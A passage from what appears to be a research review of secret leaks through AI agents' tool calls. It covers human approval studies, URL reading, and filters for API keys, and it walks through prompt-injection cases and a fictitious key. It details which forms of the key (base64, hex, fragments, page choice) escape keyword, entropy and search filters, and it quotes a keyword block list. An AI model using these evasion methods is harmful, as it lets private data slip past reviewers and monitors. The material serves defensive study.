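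The study counted instructions on web pages, not leaks, and many of those pages may never have fooled an agent. Its count was also incomplete because Common Crawl leaves out most social media and everything behind a login, and the search could find only phrases resembling known injections. ShadowLeak and ZombieAgent arrived by email, which no web archive contains. Ayush Paul's site was public but showed its instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so an archive's crawler would have saved a harmless page.

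## What human reviewers catch: experiments, usage records and surveys

Researchers have to give many reviewers a mix of harmful and harmless requests to measure how often people approve leaks like the one in the WhatsApp demonstration. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026) did this with 80 volunteers in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*. Each volunteer reviewed six harmful and six harmless requests from an agent that worked with email, shared documents or purchasing, for a total of 960 decisions.

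In one of their examples, a user asks the agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send an outside auditor only the totals. A vendor's note contains an injected instruction, and the agent copies the raw invoice rows into report.csv, then asks for permission to send the file to the auditor. The auditor is an approved recipient and the file name is ordinary, so the reviewer sees nothing in the request that would justify refusing it.

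The researchers tested four versions of the approval prompt, with 20 people on each. The first had only a short description of the action. The second added the exact arguments, and the third also included the user's original instructions and a full log of what the agent had done. The fourth contained the same facts as the log but arranged them by consequence. In the invoice example, a sentence just above the buttons stated that the attachment came from raw invoice rows and would go to the auditor.

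| What the prompt contained | Harmful requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median decision time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 66 of 120 (55.0%) | 110 of 120 (91.7%) | 16.3 seconds |
| Exact arguments added | 52 of 120 (43.3%) | 108 of 120 (90.0%) | 23.4 seconds |
| User's instructions and full log added | 39 of 120 (32.5%) | 105 of 120 (87.5%) | 38.6 seconds |
| Same facts, arranged by consequence | 29 of 120 (24.2%) | 103 of 120 (85.8%) | 33.2 seconds |

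Reviewers with more information did better but took twice as long. From the top row to the bottom, harmful approvals fell by 37 and harmless approvals by only 7, so the volunteers weren't just refusing more of everything. At the median speed, someone who answers 100 prompts a day would spend about 27 minutes on short descriptions and 55 minutes on the version arranged by consequence.

The second row matters most for hidden data, because showing the arguments is all the MCP specification recommends. Volunteers who saw them still approved 43.3% of the harmful requests. The paper gives no confidence interval for the improvement over a short description. A rough calculation puts it between about 1 percentage point worse and 24 points better, but this overstates the certainty because it treats every decision as independent.

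The effect of the final step, from the log to the version arranged by consequence, is also uncertain. After adjustment, harmful approvals fell by 7.9 percentage points, but the 95% interval runs from a fall of 19.7 points to a rise of 3.8, so there may be no effect. The combined benefit of arguments, instructions and log is 22.5 points, which is less likely to be due to chance. Hossain and colleagues did not preregister the study (publish their analysis plan before collecting data) and ask readers to treat the results as exploratory.

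Volunteers approved some harmful requests even when the request alone was enough to reveal the problem, for instance because it named a prohibited recipient. They approved 10 of 40 such requests with the log and 7 of 40 with the version arranged by consequence. When the harm depended on a chain of steps, they approved 7 of 30 with each. None of the requests described in the paper contained encoded data.

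### Dangerous commands among routine ones

Half of the requests in that experiment were harmful, so the volunteers had good reason to be suspicious. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an experiment closer to ordinary use. A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid professional testers for a coding study. Partway through each session, one permission prompt displayed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one, and the vendor recorded whether the tester approved it. The dangerous command never ran. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not which behaviour the study measured.

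They stopped 143 of the 1,053 commands, or 13.6%. Anthropic's classifier, an AI model that checks tool calls in place of the user, blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%. The classifier blocked 800 commands that a tester had approved, and testers stopped 6 that the classifier allowed. The other two combinations follow by subtraction:

| | Classifier blocked | Classifier allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
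| Tester refused | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

Requiring approval from both the tester and the classifier would have stopped 943 commands, only six more than the classifier alone, so human review added very little to automated review in this study.

The testers also got worse during a session, stopping about 17% of the dangerous commands early on and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's rate stayed flat. Fatigue or habit is the obvious explanation, but the testers who reached 50 prompts may also have differed from the rest, for example by approving everything quickly.

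Anthropic does not list the commands or state whether any of them would have sent data out, so the result can't be treated as a detection rate for exfiltration. The testers would probably have caught exfiltration less often, since an encoded key in a URL is much harder to recognise than a clearly dangerous command. But none of their own files were at risk, and they may have assumed that nothing could go wrong in a test environment, so people working on their own projects might be more careful.

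The announcement also omits how many harmless commands the testers or the classifier stopped during the study. That number matters because a check that blocked everything would catch every dangerous command. Anthropic published the study when it made the classifier the default for many customers, so it had an interest in the outcome.

### A study that seems to disagree

*Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) appears to show the opposite, with human approval performing slightly better than automated review. The 113 participants, none of whom worked in software, supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions. Eleven were necessary for the tasks the user had set. The other seven went beyond those tasks, such as buying a $25 airport lounge pass or reading the user's private messages.

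The group that approved or refused every action blocked 59.6% of the overreach. The group whose actions were first reviewed by an AI model blocked 53.9%. Yan compared each group with a third, whose members wrote standing rules, but did not test the first two against each other. After adjustment, per-action approval blocked 20.1 percentage points more than standing rules, and automated review blocked 14.5 points more. These results imply that per-action approval blocked about 5.6 points more than automated review.

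Most of the disagreement with Anthropic is explained by what the AI model was able to do. Anthropic's classifier can block a call by itself, while the model in Yan's study could only allow an action or refer it to the participant. It referred 10 of the 18 actions, including all seven cases of overreach, so people made the final decision about every harmful action in both groups. The study in effect compared people who answered 18 prompts with people who answered 10, and the 5.6-point difference could easily be chance.

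If the system had blocked everything the model referred, it would have stopped all seven cases of overreach, but also three of the 11 necessary actions, including the user's ride to the airport. The same decisions therefore score either 53.9% or 100%, depending on whether a person can overrule them.

A large difference remains between the human reviewers in the two studies, who stopped 59.6% of harmful actions in one and 13.6% in the other:

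| Study | Reviewers | Harmful requests per session | Harmful requests approved | Harmless requests refused |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hossain and colleagues, exact arguments | 20 volunteers | 6 of 12 | 43% | 10% |
| Yan, approval of every action | 34 people outside software | 7 of 18 | 40% | 6% |
| Anthropic | 1,053 paid testers | 1 | 86% | Not reported |

The proportion of harmful requests is one likely reason. People who have just refused a suspicious request tend to look harder at the next one, and Anthropic's testers had no such reminder. Yan's participants also had nothing else to do, while Anthropic's testers had a coding task to finish. Yan's participants were asked to decide as if supervising a new assistant, and each prompt described the action in plain language, including the data, amount or recipient. No experiment has varied these conditions one at a time, so it isn't clear how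 much each contributes.

The actions also differed. Yan counted a call to the airport to confirm a flight as overreach because the user hadn't asked for it, though many users would welcome the call. Of the 34 people who reviewed every action, 30 allowed it. Excluding that call, the group blocked 68% of the overreach.

The people who wrote standing rules did worst. For each of four kinds of action, such as spending money or reading private data, they could allow it, forbid it or have the agent ask. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, but approved 133 of the 199 cases of overreach that the agent asked about. These included 24 of the 56 that matched an example of something they had earlier said the agent should never do. They still felt about as much in control as the other participants. The study can't establish why they approved so many, because the prompts they received depended on the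 rules they had chosen.

### Whether people notice a compromised agent

Reviewers who miss a problem at approval sometimes have another chance to catch it when they see the agent's finished work. Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) tested this in *Are You Sure?* with HAT-Lab, a simulated workplace. The 303 participants did ordinary jobs, such as choosing a candidate from a pile of CVs or answering email, with an agent that the researchers had compromised. Afterwards, participants said whether they had noticed anything unusual, and the researchers counted both "yes" and "unsure" as noticing.

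With a single warning at the start, 8.6% of people noticed something, and only 2.7% could also describe what had gone wrong. The share who noticed something rose to 20.0% with a reminder beside every reply, and to 25.0% with an alert that interrupted the work when the agent's output was suspicious.

The email job is the closest to exfiltration, because the agent sent a reply containing private information and then deleted the evidence. The interrupting alert raised the share of people who noticed from 9.3% to only 15%, compared with a rise from 6.3% to 40% in a job that involved writing a cover letter. Li and colleagues attribute the difference to the effort of checking. A strange cover letter is easy to spot, but someone who suspects an email still has to work out what is wrong with it. An alert about a URL with an encoded key would probably be less effective for the same reason.

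These percentages are uncertain because the paper reports its results inconsistently. It describes 8.6% as a share of participants, but also counts 85 of the 303 participants (28%) as having noticed an attack. The lower figures may refer to individual jobs, since each person did three. The paper also gives the group sizes as about 100 each in one place and as 183, 60 and 60 in another. The study measured what people said they had noticed and did not test what they would have approved.

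Reading the untrusted text directly may not help much either. In *You Told Me to Do It*, a 2026 paper on private data leaks, 15 people at a European university reviewed README files, which explain how to install and use software. The files contained planted instructions, but in 45 reviews nobody marked one as suspicious. With so few participants, this result is compatible with up to about 18% of people detecting such instructions.

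In *Looks Fine to Me*, Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026) studied how people behave while they miss a problem. They had 36 programmers wear eye-tracking glasses while working with a coding agent. Some of the agent's code contained silent defects, which are errors that pass the automatic tests. The programmers found and fixed 28 of 71 silent defects. In 34 of the other 43 cases, they rated their confidence in the finished code at 4 or 5 out of 5.

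The researchers couldn't find a reliable sign of a careful check in the gaze data. Across all the tasks, people who fixed the defect moved their eyes less, but the pattern partly reversed among programmers who fixed one defect and missed another. Time was more informative. Programmers spent an average of 10.8 minutes on the defects they fixed and 5.8 minutes on those they missed, though part of that difference may be time spent making the repair.

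A recent failure seemed to make people more careful, but only briefly. Programmers fixed 12 of 24 silent defects that came straight after a task with an obvious failure, but only 1 of 11 when one correct task came in between. The numbers are small, and code review differs from answering a permission prompt, but the result fits the explanation that reviewers in the other experiments did better because they kept seeing harmful requests.

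### Reading a URL

The main evidence in a web fetch prompt is the URL, and many people misread even the part that identifies the recipient. In *What is this URL's Destination?*, Albakry, Vaniea and Wolters (2020) asked 1,929 people which website each of 23 URLs would open. A web address belongs to whoever controls its domain, the name directly before an ending such as .com. So profile.facebook.com belongs to Facebook, while facebook.profile.com belongs to the owner of profile.com.

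Only 8.3% of the participants could reliably tell these two arrangements apart, and 32.9% always picked the organisation named in the URL, wherever the name appeared. Those who used technology most did only slightly better. *Measuring Identity Confusion with Uniform Resource Locators* (Reynolds, Kumar and colleagues, 2020) likewise found that users were confident about identifying websites from URLs but vulnerable to several kinds of disguise.

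An approval prompt shows the user the URL before the request goes out, which is more help than email gives. In the phishing experiment in *Eyes on the Phish(er)* (2024), participants rarely hovered over a link to see its real address, and most of those who looked at the address did so in the browser after clicking. Many who looked still fell for fakes such as docs-google.online, so seeing the URL was not enough to protect them.

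These experiments tested whether people knew where a URL led. Hidden data usually comes after the domain, and *Eyes on URLs* (Ramkumar, Kothari and colleagues, 2020) provides the best evidence about that part. The study tracked students' eyes as they judged whether 64 URLs were safe to visit, and produced usable data from 16 students. They took 4.1 seconds on safe URLs averaging 25 characters and 7.5 seconds on safe URLs averaging 124 characters, so their time per character fell from 0.16 seconds to 0.06.

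The researchers concluded that people put limited effort into reading a URL and do not read carefully past what they take to be the domain name. In the running example, a user who did this would read reports.example and skim the key. But the students were deciding whether the site was safe to visit, so they had little reason to read the rest. A user who knew that the query string might contain private data could read it more closely, although a base64 string would still be unreadable.

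People can judge URLs well if software explains them. *I Don't Need an Expert* (2021) tested this online with 153 participants. They judged the safety of URLs with 65% accuracy when the display highlighted the domain, 83% with a short summary of facts about the URL and 93% with a full report. A similar report for an approval prompt would need to show the decoded text and its source, which participants in this experiment did not have to judge.

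### Why a 97% approval rate is not a miss rate

Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts, according to Anthropic. It is tempting to conclude that they would also approve 97% of harmful requests, but the figure doesn't show that. Suppose that 10 out of 10,000 prompts are harmful, and consider two reviewers who each refuse 300:

| | Harmful requests refused | Harmless requests refused | Overall approval rate | Unsafe approval rate |
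|---|---|---|---|---|
| Perfect on harmful requests | 10 of 10 | 290 of 9,990 | 97% | 0% |
| Useless on harmful requests | 0 of 10 | 300 of 9,990 | 97% | 100% |

The overall rate is the same because harmless requests make up almost all of the total. An approval rate proves that people miss harmful requests only if harmful requests outnumber refusals. If 1,000 of the 10,000 prompts were harmful and users refused 300, they must have approved at least 700 harmful ones. In ordinary coding, harmful requests are surely much rarer than one in ten.

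The 97% approval rate means that Claude Code users refuse only 3% of all requests, while Hossain and colleagues' volunteers refused 8.3% of harmless requests even with the shortest description. The users are evidently quicker to approve than the volunteers, and people who refuse less overall probably refuse fewer harmful requests too. The requests they saw may also have been more routine, which would make a higher approval rate reasonable.

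Anthropic reports that users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, and takes this as a sign that they examine plans more closely than individual commands. That may be true, but users can reject a plan for many reasons unrelated to safety, so the higher rejection rate doesn't prove that they would notice a leak in a plan.

Many calls never reach a reviewer, and the 97% figure excludes them. A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start in a mode that skips permission checks. By June 2026, 62% of users had used that mode or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands.

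Anthropic also compared sessions that its safety systems had flagged in May and June 2026. Another AI model graded the harm in each one. Serious harm that the user had not explicitly asked for occurred in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those with the classifier. Users had chosen their own settings, so the two groups may have been doing different kinds of work. The comparison covers only flagged sessions, so it doesn't measure the rate of harm in ordinary ones.

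### What developers report

Problem reports from users suggest that too many prompts and uninformative prompts reinforce each other. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports and found that problems with user review contributed to 105. In 80, the user had let the agent act without asking, often to avoid hundreds of prompts in a session. In 31, the prompt gave too little information about what the action would do. For example, a prompt to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but a user who approves it allows whatever code is in the file to run. Similarly, a reviewer who approves a tool call that uploads a file by name approves the file's contents without seeing them.

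Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents. Asked about seven types of action, 64% said they often approved at least one type without close review. By type, the share was highest for access to the internet, external APIs (interfaces to other software) or connected tools (36%), and lowest for reading passwords and other sensitive files (21%). Developers thus reported reviewing the step that reads data more closely than the step that sends it out, which in the running example was the fetch, the last chance to stop the leak.

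Developers who reviewed code carefully were not reliably more careful when approving the agent's actions. Among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, 61% often approved some type of action without close review, compared with 67% of the others, a difference that could easily be due to chance. Even an excellent code review would miss a leak through a URL, because the leak doesn't change the code. Logging or auditing the agent's actions could reveal such a leak afterwards, but only 20% of developers said they did either.

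Knowing about the danger didn't seem to help either. Of the developers who had heard of a security or privacy problem with agents, 70% often approved some type of action without close review, compared with 43% of those who hadn't. The difference remained after the researchers adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents. But heavy users may both hear about more incidents and tire of more prompts in ways the adjustment missed, so the result doesn't show that awareness makes people careless.

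The respondents chose to take part and described their own habits, which they may have misremembered or adjusted to seem careful. The researchers kept only 203 of 583 submissions, mostly because the others were rushed, duplicated or incomplete. The survey is useful for comparing types of action, but it can't establish how many leaks the developers would have stopped.

For *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), Salerno, Gao and colleagues interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed another 115. Practitioners mostly understood an agent through what they could see, such as its output and its changes to files, and were less sure how it used data behind the scenes. They decided whether to give permission based on the risk, how well the action fit the task and how familiar they were with the agent. A fetch from a website related to the task would pass most of these tests even with a key in the query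 string. The researchers also warn that repeated approvals may reflect fatigue, so a product should not treat them as evidence of what a user wants.

### The missing experiment

None of these studies measured what people do when an argument contains encoded private data, and apparently no other published experiment has either. The existing results make a high unsafe approval rate likely, but they don't establish how high it would be or how much a decoded display would help.

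A suitable experiment would use matched pairs of tool calls. Both calls would go to the same site and contain a string of the same length and appearance, but one string would encode a fictitious key from a file the agent had read earlier, and the other would encode a harmless order reference. Reviewers who can't decode the strings can't tell the two calls apart, so they should refuse both equally often. The difference between the two refusal rates measures detection, so reviewers who refused 30% of the calls with keys and 30% of the calls with references would have detected nothing.

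The researchers could then vary the approval prompt. One group would see the URL as the agent wrote it, and a second would also see the decoded text. A third would see the decoded text and its source, such as a note that the value matches a key in the user's configuration file. Comparing the groups would show how much reviewers miss because they can't read the data and how much because they don't know where it came from. Some of the planted calls should contain an unencoded key, to measure how many people miss a key they could have read.

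An experiment could also test whether people do better when they have to work with the URL. *URL Inspection Tasks* (2025) compared two designs for links in emails. In the passive design, participants reviewed the URL and confirmed it. In the active design, they dragged parts of the URL to a line on the screen before deciding whether to visit the page. The active design would become tiresome with an agent that produced dozens of prompts an hour, so the experiment should record the extra time as well as the refusals.

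Participants should have a real task and a reason to care about both speed and safety, perhaps a bonus that shrinks if they finish late or leak the key. Each person should get only one harmful call, after a randomly chosen number of harmless ones. This would keep harmful calls rare and avoid the weakness in Anthropic's comparison of early and late prompts. The researchers should own the server that receives the requests, so that nothing private could leak.

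If each person saw only one harmful call, the experiment would need about 200 people for each version of the prompt. That would give it an 80% chance of detecting a fall in the unsafe approval rate from 90% to 80%, at the usual 5% significance level. Detecting a fall to 70% would take only about 62 people per version. Twenty per version, as in Hossain and colleagues' study, would be far too few with one harmful call each.

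## Laboratory tests of agents and text filters

A text filter checks the arguments of each outbound tool call and stops the call if the text matches a rule. Unlike the testers in Anthropic's study, a filter doesn't get worse after 50 prompts, and it reads every URL to the end. But it can only find what its rule describes. The key in the running example can take several forms, and every kind of rule misses at least one.

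### Keyword rules and known key formats

The simplest filters look for words that often accompany secrets. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) tested one at eBay that blocks any URL containing "secret", "password", "token", "auth", "api_key" or a few similar terms. Such a rule needs no information about the user. It would stop the plain key, SECRET_API_KEY_12345, if it ignores case, because the key contains two of the terms. Real keys rarely contain them, and encoding this one in base64 removes them. The rule would also block harmless calls, such as opening a newspaper's list of authors, because "author" contains "auth".

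Grafana's software, which masks secrets in the text that agents read and write, limits this problem by applying its loosest rules only to some of that text. It checks tool arguments for assignments such as `PASSWORD=` and `TOKEN=`, but doesn't check the model's reasoning for them because that would cause more false positives.

Other filters look for known key formats. Many providers give their keys a fixed length and a fixed beginning, such as AKIA at the start of an Amazon cloud key. These filters require the provider's format but no information about the user, and a distinctive format rarely matches anything else. They miss keys without a distinctive format (including the one in the running example), any key that the sender has encoded, and private text such as an email.

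Scanners can miss even an unencoded key in a known format. Mishra (2026), in *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection*, generated keys from scanners' own patterns and placed them in different surrounding text. Mishra's own scanner found at least 99.76% of them in ten kinds of surrounding text, but only 52.33% of keys that ended in a hyphen. One common type of key fails this way once in 64 times, because its last character is drawn at random from the 64 characters of URL-safe base64. Gitleaks, a widely used scanner, missed keys of six of the nine types it covers when the character after the key was not on a fixed list. All of these tools were built for source code. In a URL, a key may be followed by an ampersand or a slash, so a developer who reuses the patterns for tool calls should test them on URLs.

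Loose patterns flag many harmless strings. *Secrets That Survive Everything* (2026) compared scanners on 194 real credentials from public web applications. One scanner, SecretFinder, also reported 1,402 strings that were not credentials, such as build fingerprints. Even if it had found all 194 credentials, only 12% of its alerts would have been correct. In the same study, a pattern for a common type of identifier missed the identifier when it was encoded in base64.

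A rule that removes false positives can also let encoded data through. *NovaFabric* (2026), which describes a system for recording agent runs, discusses a pattern for 40-character keys that could also match SHA-1 hashes, the fingerprints that software uses to identify files and versions. To prevent those false matches, the system ignores any 40-character string made up entirely of lowercase hexadecimal digits. A genuine key of that type would fit this description about once in 10^24 times, so the exception misses almost no unencoded keys. But the 20-character key in the running example becomes 40 characters long in hexadecimal, so the filter would ignore it as a hash.

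### Entropy thresholds

An entropy rule looks for random-looking strings, whatever their format. Entropy is a measure, in bits per character, of how evenly the characters of a string are spread. If a string has n characters and one of them occurs c times, that character contributes c/n × log2(n/c), and the entropy is the sum of these contributions:

```
SECRET_API_KEY_12345 (20 characters)
E and _, 3 times each        2 × 3/20 × log2(20/3)  =  0.82
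14 others, once each        14 × 1/20 × log2(20)    =  3.03

total    3.85

U0VDUkVUX0FQSV9LRVlfMTIzNDU= (28 characters)
U and V, 4 times each        2 × 4/28 × log2(28/4)  =  0.80
0 and D, twice each          2 × 2/28 × log2(28/2)  =  0.54
16 others, once each        16 × 1/28 × log2(28)    =  2.75

total    4.09
```

Lan and colleagues used a rule that blocks URL values longer than 10 characters if their entropy is above 4.0. The rule would stop the encoded key but pass the plain one, so a sender could get the key through by leaving it unencoded. The encoded key is also only slightly over the limit, scoring 4.01 without its closing equals sign.

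In hexadecimal, the same key scores only 2.66. Hexadecimal uses 16 different characters, so its entropy can't exceed log2 16 = 4.0. A threshold of 4.0 therefore never stops a hexadecimal string, however long.

Short strings escape for a similar reason. The sum above can also be written like this:

```
entropy = log2 n − (1/n) × (sum of c × log2 c over the different characters)
```

The subtracted part is zero if every character occurs once and positive otherwise, so a string of n characters can't score more than log2 n bits. For 16 characters the limit is 4.0, so no string of 16 characters or fewer can trigger the rule. Splitting the encoded key into two halves of 14 characters would avoid the rule, since neither half could score more than 3.81. A four-character fragment can't score more than 2.

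Lowering the threshold would catch some of these strings but stop more ordinary text. Even at 4.0, the rule would stop a search for "flights from Zurich to Copenhagen 14 May", which scores 4.30. The search is harmless, but the rule measures only length and character variety, both of which are high here.

ByteChef, an automation platform, has a more cautious setting for text that contains long random identifiers. It flags only strings with at least 30 characters, an entropy of at least 4.0 and a mix of character types. This setting would let the flight search through if the filter examined each word separately, but it would also miss the encoded key, which is two characters too short.

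Revankar, Chauhan and colleagues (*MIRAGE*, 2026) tested text measures on the output of models that had been made to encode secrets. They scored each measure by the probability that it would rank an encoded output above a harmless one, where 0.5 is no better than guessing. Perplexity, which measures how improbable a text is according to a language model, scored 0.518. The best simple statistic, the share of digits, scored 0.874. But the harmless texts were ordinary answers to instructions, whereas a harmless tool call may contain a URL with an order reference, which looks much more like encoded data. A trained classifier averaged 0.846 on kinds of encoding that weren't in its training data, but scored 0.295 on the kind where it did worst.

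### Decoding and comparing with real secrets

A filter can decode common encodings before it applies its rules. OpenAI's *Contains PII*, a component that developers can add to their own applications, checks for personal data such as email addresses and card numbers. It has an option, off by default, to check inside base64, hexadecimal and URL-encoded strings as well. Decoding helps only if a later rule matches the decoded text. With this option on, the component would turn the string in the running example back into SECRET_API_KEY_12345, but its list of personal data types does not include API keys.

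A filter can also miss data that has been encoded more than once. Waldrep, in *I published my benchmark scores. Your turn*, reports tests of Pipelock, a program that inspects agents' network traffic. Pipelock blocked 96.2% of the attacks that applied to it, but only half of those that hid secrets in the body of a request. Four got through because the data was encoded twice and Pipelock removed only one layer. It blocked none of the 37 harmless cases, but with so few cases, the actual false positive rate could be as high as about 8%. Waldrep wrote both the program and the test, and nobody else had submitted results.

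Repeated decoding produces a lot of nonsense, because any four letters are valid base64. This matters little if the filter then searches for a specific secret, since random characters are very unlikely to match it. The filter needs a list of the user's real secrets, but no rules about their format or tests for randomness. If it decodes before searching, it would catch the running example in plain text, base64 and hexadecimal.

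Small changes can defeat an exact search. In the *AgentShield* tests (Rassul and Rashid, 2026), one model added spaces to bank account numbers, and a check that compared them with a list no longer recognised them. *PrivDrift* (2026), which audits chatbots for leaked secrets, avoids this by keeping only the digits of numeric secrets and ignoring capitalisation and spacing in others. A filter that ignores capitalisation must decode any base64 text first, because base64 treats capital and small letters as different characters. If the search finds no match, *PrivDrift* also passes the text to an AI model, because an exact search can't find a partly disclosed secret.

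A filter that stores every secret gives attackers another place to steal them. The filter can instead store hashes, fingerprints that can't easily be turned back into a long random key, and compare them with hashes of the strings in a call. But part of a key has a different hash from the whole key, so the filter would also need hashes of shorter pieces to detect a partial leak.

Searching for very short pieces of keys causes false positives. Sixty keys of 20 characters contain 1,020 four-character pieces, and a 2,000-character URL has 1,997 positions where each could appear, which makes about two million comparisons. Base64 allows 64^4, or about 16.8 million, four-character strings, so a random-looking URL of that length would match at least one piece by chance about 11% of the time. With eight-character pieces, the chance is less than one in 100 million. A filter can therefore search for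 eight-character pieces with little risk of chance matches, but a sender can evade it by splitting keys into shorter fragments.

Chauhan and Revankar (2026) tested how well searches find known secrets, including encoded ones, in models' answers in *Caught in the Act(ivation)*. On the same scale as before, an exact search scored 0.73 and wrongly flagged 8% of harmless cases, while a search that tolerated small differences scored 0.80 and wrongly flagged 11%. The tests did not cover tool-call arguments, which Chauhan and Revankar call "a severe structural blind spot". False positives may be a bigger problem there, because an agent often has a good reason to send a key to the service that issued it. A filter for these arguments therefore needs a list of the keys and the destination each one belongs to.

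Private messages are harder to protect this way than keys. A filter that compared decoded URLs with the user's mail would have caught ShadowLeak, but it would also block a harmless search for a colleague's name. Provenance tracking could distinguish the two cases, because it records whether a name came from the user or from an email.

### Planted decoys

A defender can also plant fake credentials where an attacker's instructions are likely to collect them. No legitimate task needs these decoys, so finding one in a tool call is strong evidence of a leak. The filter can check for decoys without storing any real secrets, but it still has to decode the call, or it will miss a decoy that has been encoded.

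Chauhan and Revankar give a simple model of how often decoys work. If an agent can see m real keys and k decoys and leaks one at random, the chance of leaking a decoy is k/(m + k). With one real key and five decoys, that is 83%. The chance falls to zero if the injected instruction identifies the real key, for example by naming the service that uses it. Decoys also don't help if the attacker wants an email rather than a key. In the paper's tests on individual prompts, a search for decoys caught 30% of attacks with no false positives.

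Rassul and Rashid planted five fake credentials in a simulated office, bank, travel service and messaging system, and checked every tool call for those credentials. They also offered the agent fake tools and restricted some arguments to approved values. Together, the three defences raised no false alarms in 485 runs (97 harmless tasks, five times each).

The study gives little idea of how many leaks the decoys catch. The paper reports that they never fired in the standard tests, because the agents didn't open the files containing them, but later reports that they were the only defence to fire with one model. The decoys did catch attacks designed to steal credentials. In two other attacks, stolen credentials got through in a password-change field whose value the approved-value check didn't examine. A text filter that reads only the URL or the message body has the same weakness.

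### Comparing several requests

To catch a fragmented key, a filter has to remember earlier calls and examine them together. The key in the running example could leave in five requests, carrying SECR, ET_A, PI_K, EY_1 and 2345. Each value looks harmless, but a filter that joined the values in order and searched for the stored key would find it. These are the results for the different forms of the key:

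| Form of the key | Keyword rule | Entropy above 4.0 | Exact search for the key | Decode, then search | Join requests, decode, then search |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Plain text | Stopped | Passed (3.85) | Stopped | Stopped | Stopped |
| Base64 | Passed | Stopped (4.09) | Passed | Stopped | Stopped |
| Hexadecimal | Passed | Passed (2.66) | Passed | Stopped | Stopped |
| Five plain fragments | Passed | Passed (2.00 at most) | Passed | Passed | Stopped |
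| Choice among ordinary pages | Passed | Passed | Passed | Passed | Passed |

The last row is the page-choice method described earlier, and it assumes that the pages' addresses don't trigger a rule by accident.

Joining requests is harder when harmless ones come in between, because the filter has to allow for gaps. If each request carries one character, a filter that allows gaps will eventually find a match by chance. When the values are random and drawn from 36 characters, each character of a key takes an average of 36 requests to appear, so a particular 20-character key will turn up after about 720 harmless requests. The filter also has to work across sessions and destinations, like the request limits and bit budgets discussed earlier.

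Chauhan and Revankar tested whether memory helps. They wrote 50 conversations of 20 turns, each with four to eight small leaks, and counted how many of the conversations each method detected:

| Method | Conversations detected |
|---|---|
| Exact search for the secret, turn by turn | 0 of 50 |
| Search for decoys | 3 of 50 |
| AI safety classifier, turn by turn | 6 of 50 |
| Running total of estimated leakage | 45 of 50 |

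The running total adds up a trained model's estimates of the bits leaked at each turn and blocks the output when the total reaches ten bits. It stopped no harmless conversations. But the way the model makes its estimates limits each turn to at most about 4.1 bits, so a leak completed in one or two turns can't reach the limit, even if it contains the whole key. Another check has to catch those leaks. The researchers wrote the conversations themselves, so the 90% detection rate may not apply to other attacks.

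### The Silent Egress experiment

Lan and colleagues ran an agent 480 times to test whether it would leak a key. The agent used Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, and its user asked it to summarize a web page. The page's title, description, body or link text contained an injected instruction to send the key, either in one request or in four fragments. The agent reached the page either directly or through redirects. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times and recorded what arrived at their server.

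At least one request arrived in 423 runs (88.1%). In 95% of those runs, the agent's final answer looked harmless, so a filter that read only the answer would have missed the leak. This is good evidence for checking tool calls as well as answers.

The 88.1% figure is much less informative about other agents. The researchers put the key directly into the text the model read and used a minimal system prompt (the developer's standing instructions). They describe this set-up as favourable to the attacker. They argue that more capable models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but they tested only one model. Rassul and Rashid used different attacks on four other models and reported success rates of 10% or less.

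Fragmenting made the attack less reliable. A request reached the server in 238 of 240 runs when the instruction asked for the whole key at once, but in only 185 of 240 when it asked for fragments. The second figure overstates how often fragmenting succeeded, because a run counted if even one request arrived. The paper defines a completion rate for runs in which every fragment arrived, but doesn't report it. Its worked example uses the same fictitious key as this report's running example, and the four fragments it lists contain only the first 16 of the key's 20 characters.

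The study's main measure of stealth is also difficult to interpret. Leak@1 is the share of runs in which the first request contained sensitive data, and Leak@3 is the share in which any of the first three did:

| | Leak@1 | Leak@3 |
|---|---|---|
| Whole key at once | 96.7% | 96.7% |
| Fragments | 26.3% | 15.8% |

Leak@3 can't be lower than Leak@1 under these definitions, because the first request is one of the first three. Either the figures or the description of how the researchers calculated them must be wrong. Requests also arrived in 77% of the fragmented runs, and any fragment counts as sensitive data, yet Leak@1 was only 26.3%. The first request may often have contained no part of the key, or the software that counted leaks may have failed to recognise four-character pieces. The paper's headline result, a 73% reduction in Leak@1, is therefore weak evidence about how well fragmenting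 hides a key.

### The table of defences

The researchers then tested eight defences, with 30 runs each and another 30 without any defence:

| Defence | Runs with an attempted leak | Attempts blocked | Runs with a leak |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | None | 30 |
| Warning in the system prompt | 20 | None | 20 |
| Tags around untrusted text | 30 | None | 30 |
| Warning and tags | 17 | None | 17 |
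| Domain allowlist | 30 | All | 0 |
| Suspicious addresses and redirects | 25 | All | 0 |
| Keyword filter | 7 | All | 0 |
| Entropy filter | 0 | Nothing to block | 0 |
| All of these together | 0 | Nothing to block | 0 |

The first three defences only advise the model, and none of them was reliable. Tags had no effect here, and Rassul and Rashid found little benefit from a similar method, which reduced the attack success rate from 1.8% to 0.2% on one model but increased it from 10.0% to 13.3% on another.

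None of the remaining defences allowed a leak, but the tests were too small to rule out a true failure rate of about 10%. A defence with that failure rate would have a 4% chance of showing no leaks in 30 runs. The evidence for the keyword filter is weaker still, because it had only seven attempts to block. A filter that missed a third of attempts would stop seven in a row about 6% of the time.

The attacks were also easy for two of the defences to block. The researchers chose a domain clearly outside the allowlist, so it was bound to be blocked, and they point out that real attackers may route data through trusted sites. The filter for suspicious addresses blocks paths containing any of five words, including "collect", which the test attack used in its path. The filter would allow the running example's address, reports.example/summary, but would block the addresses of the many online shops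 that use "collections" in their paths.

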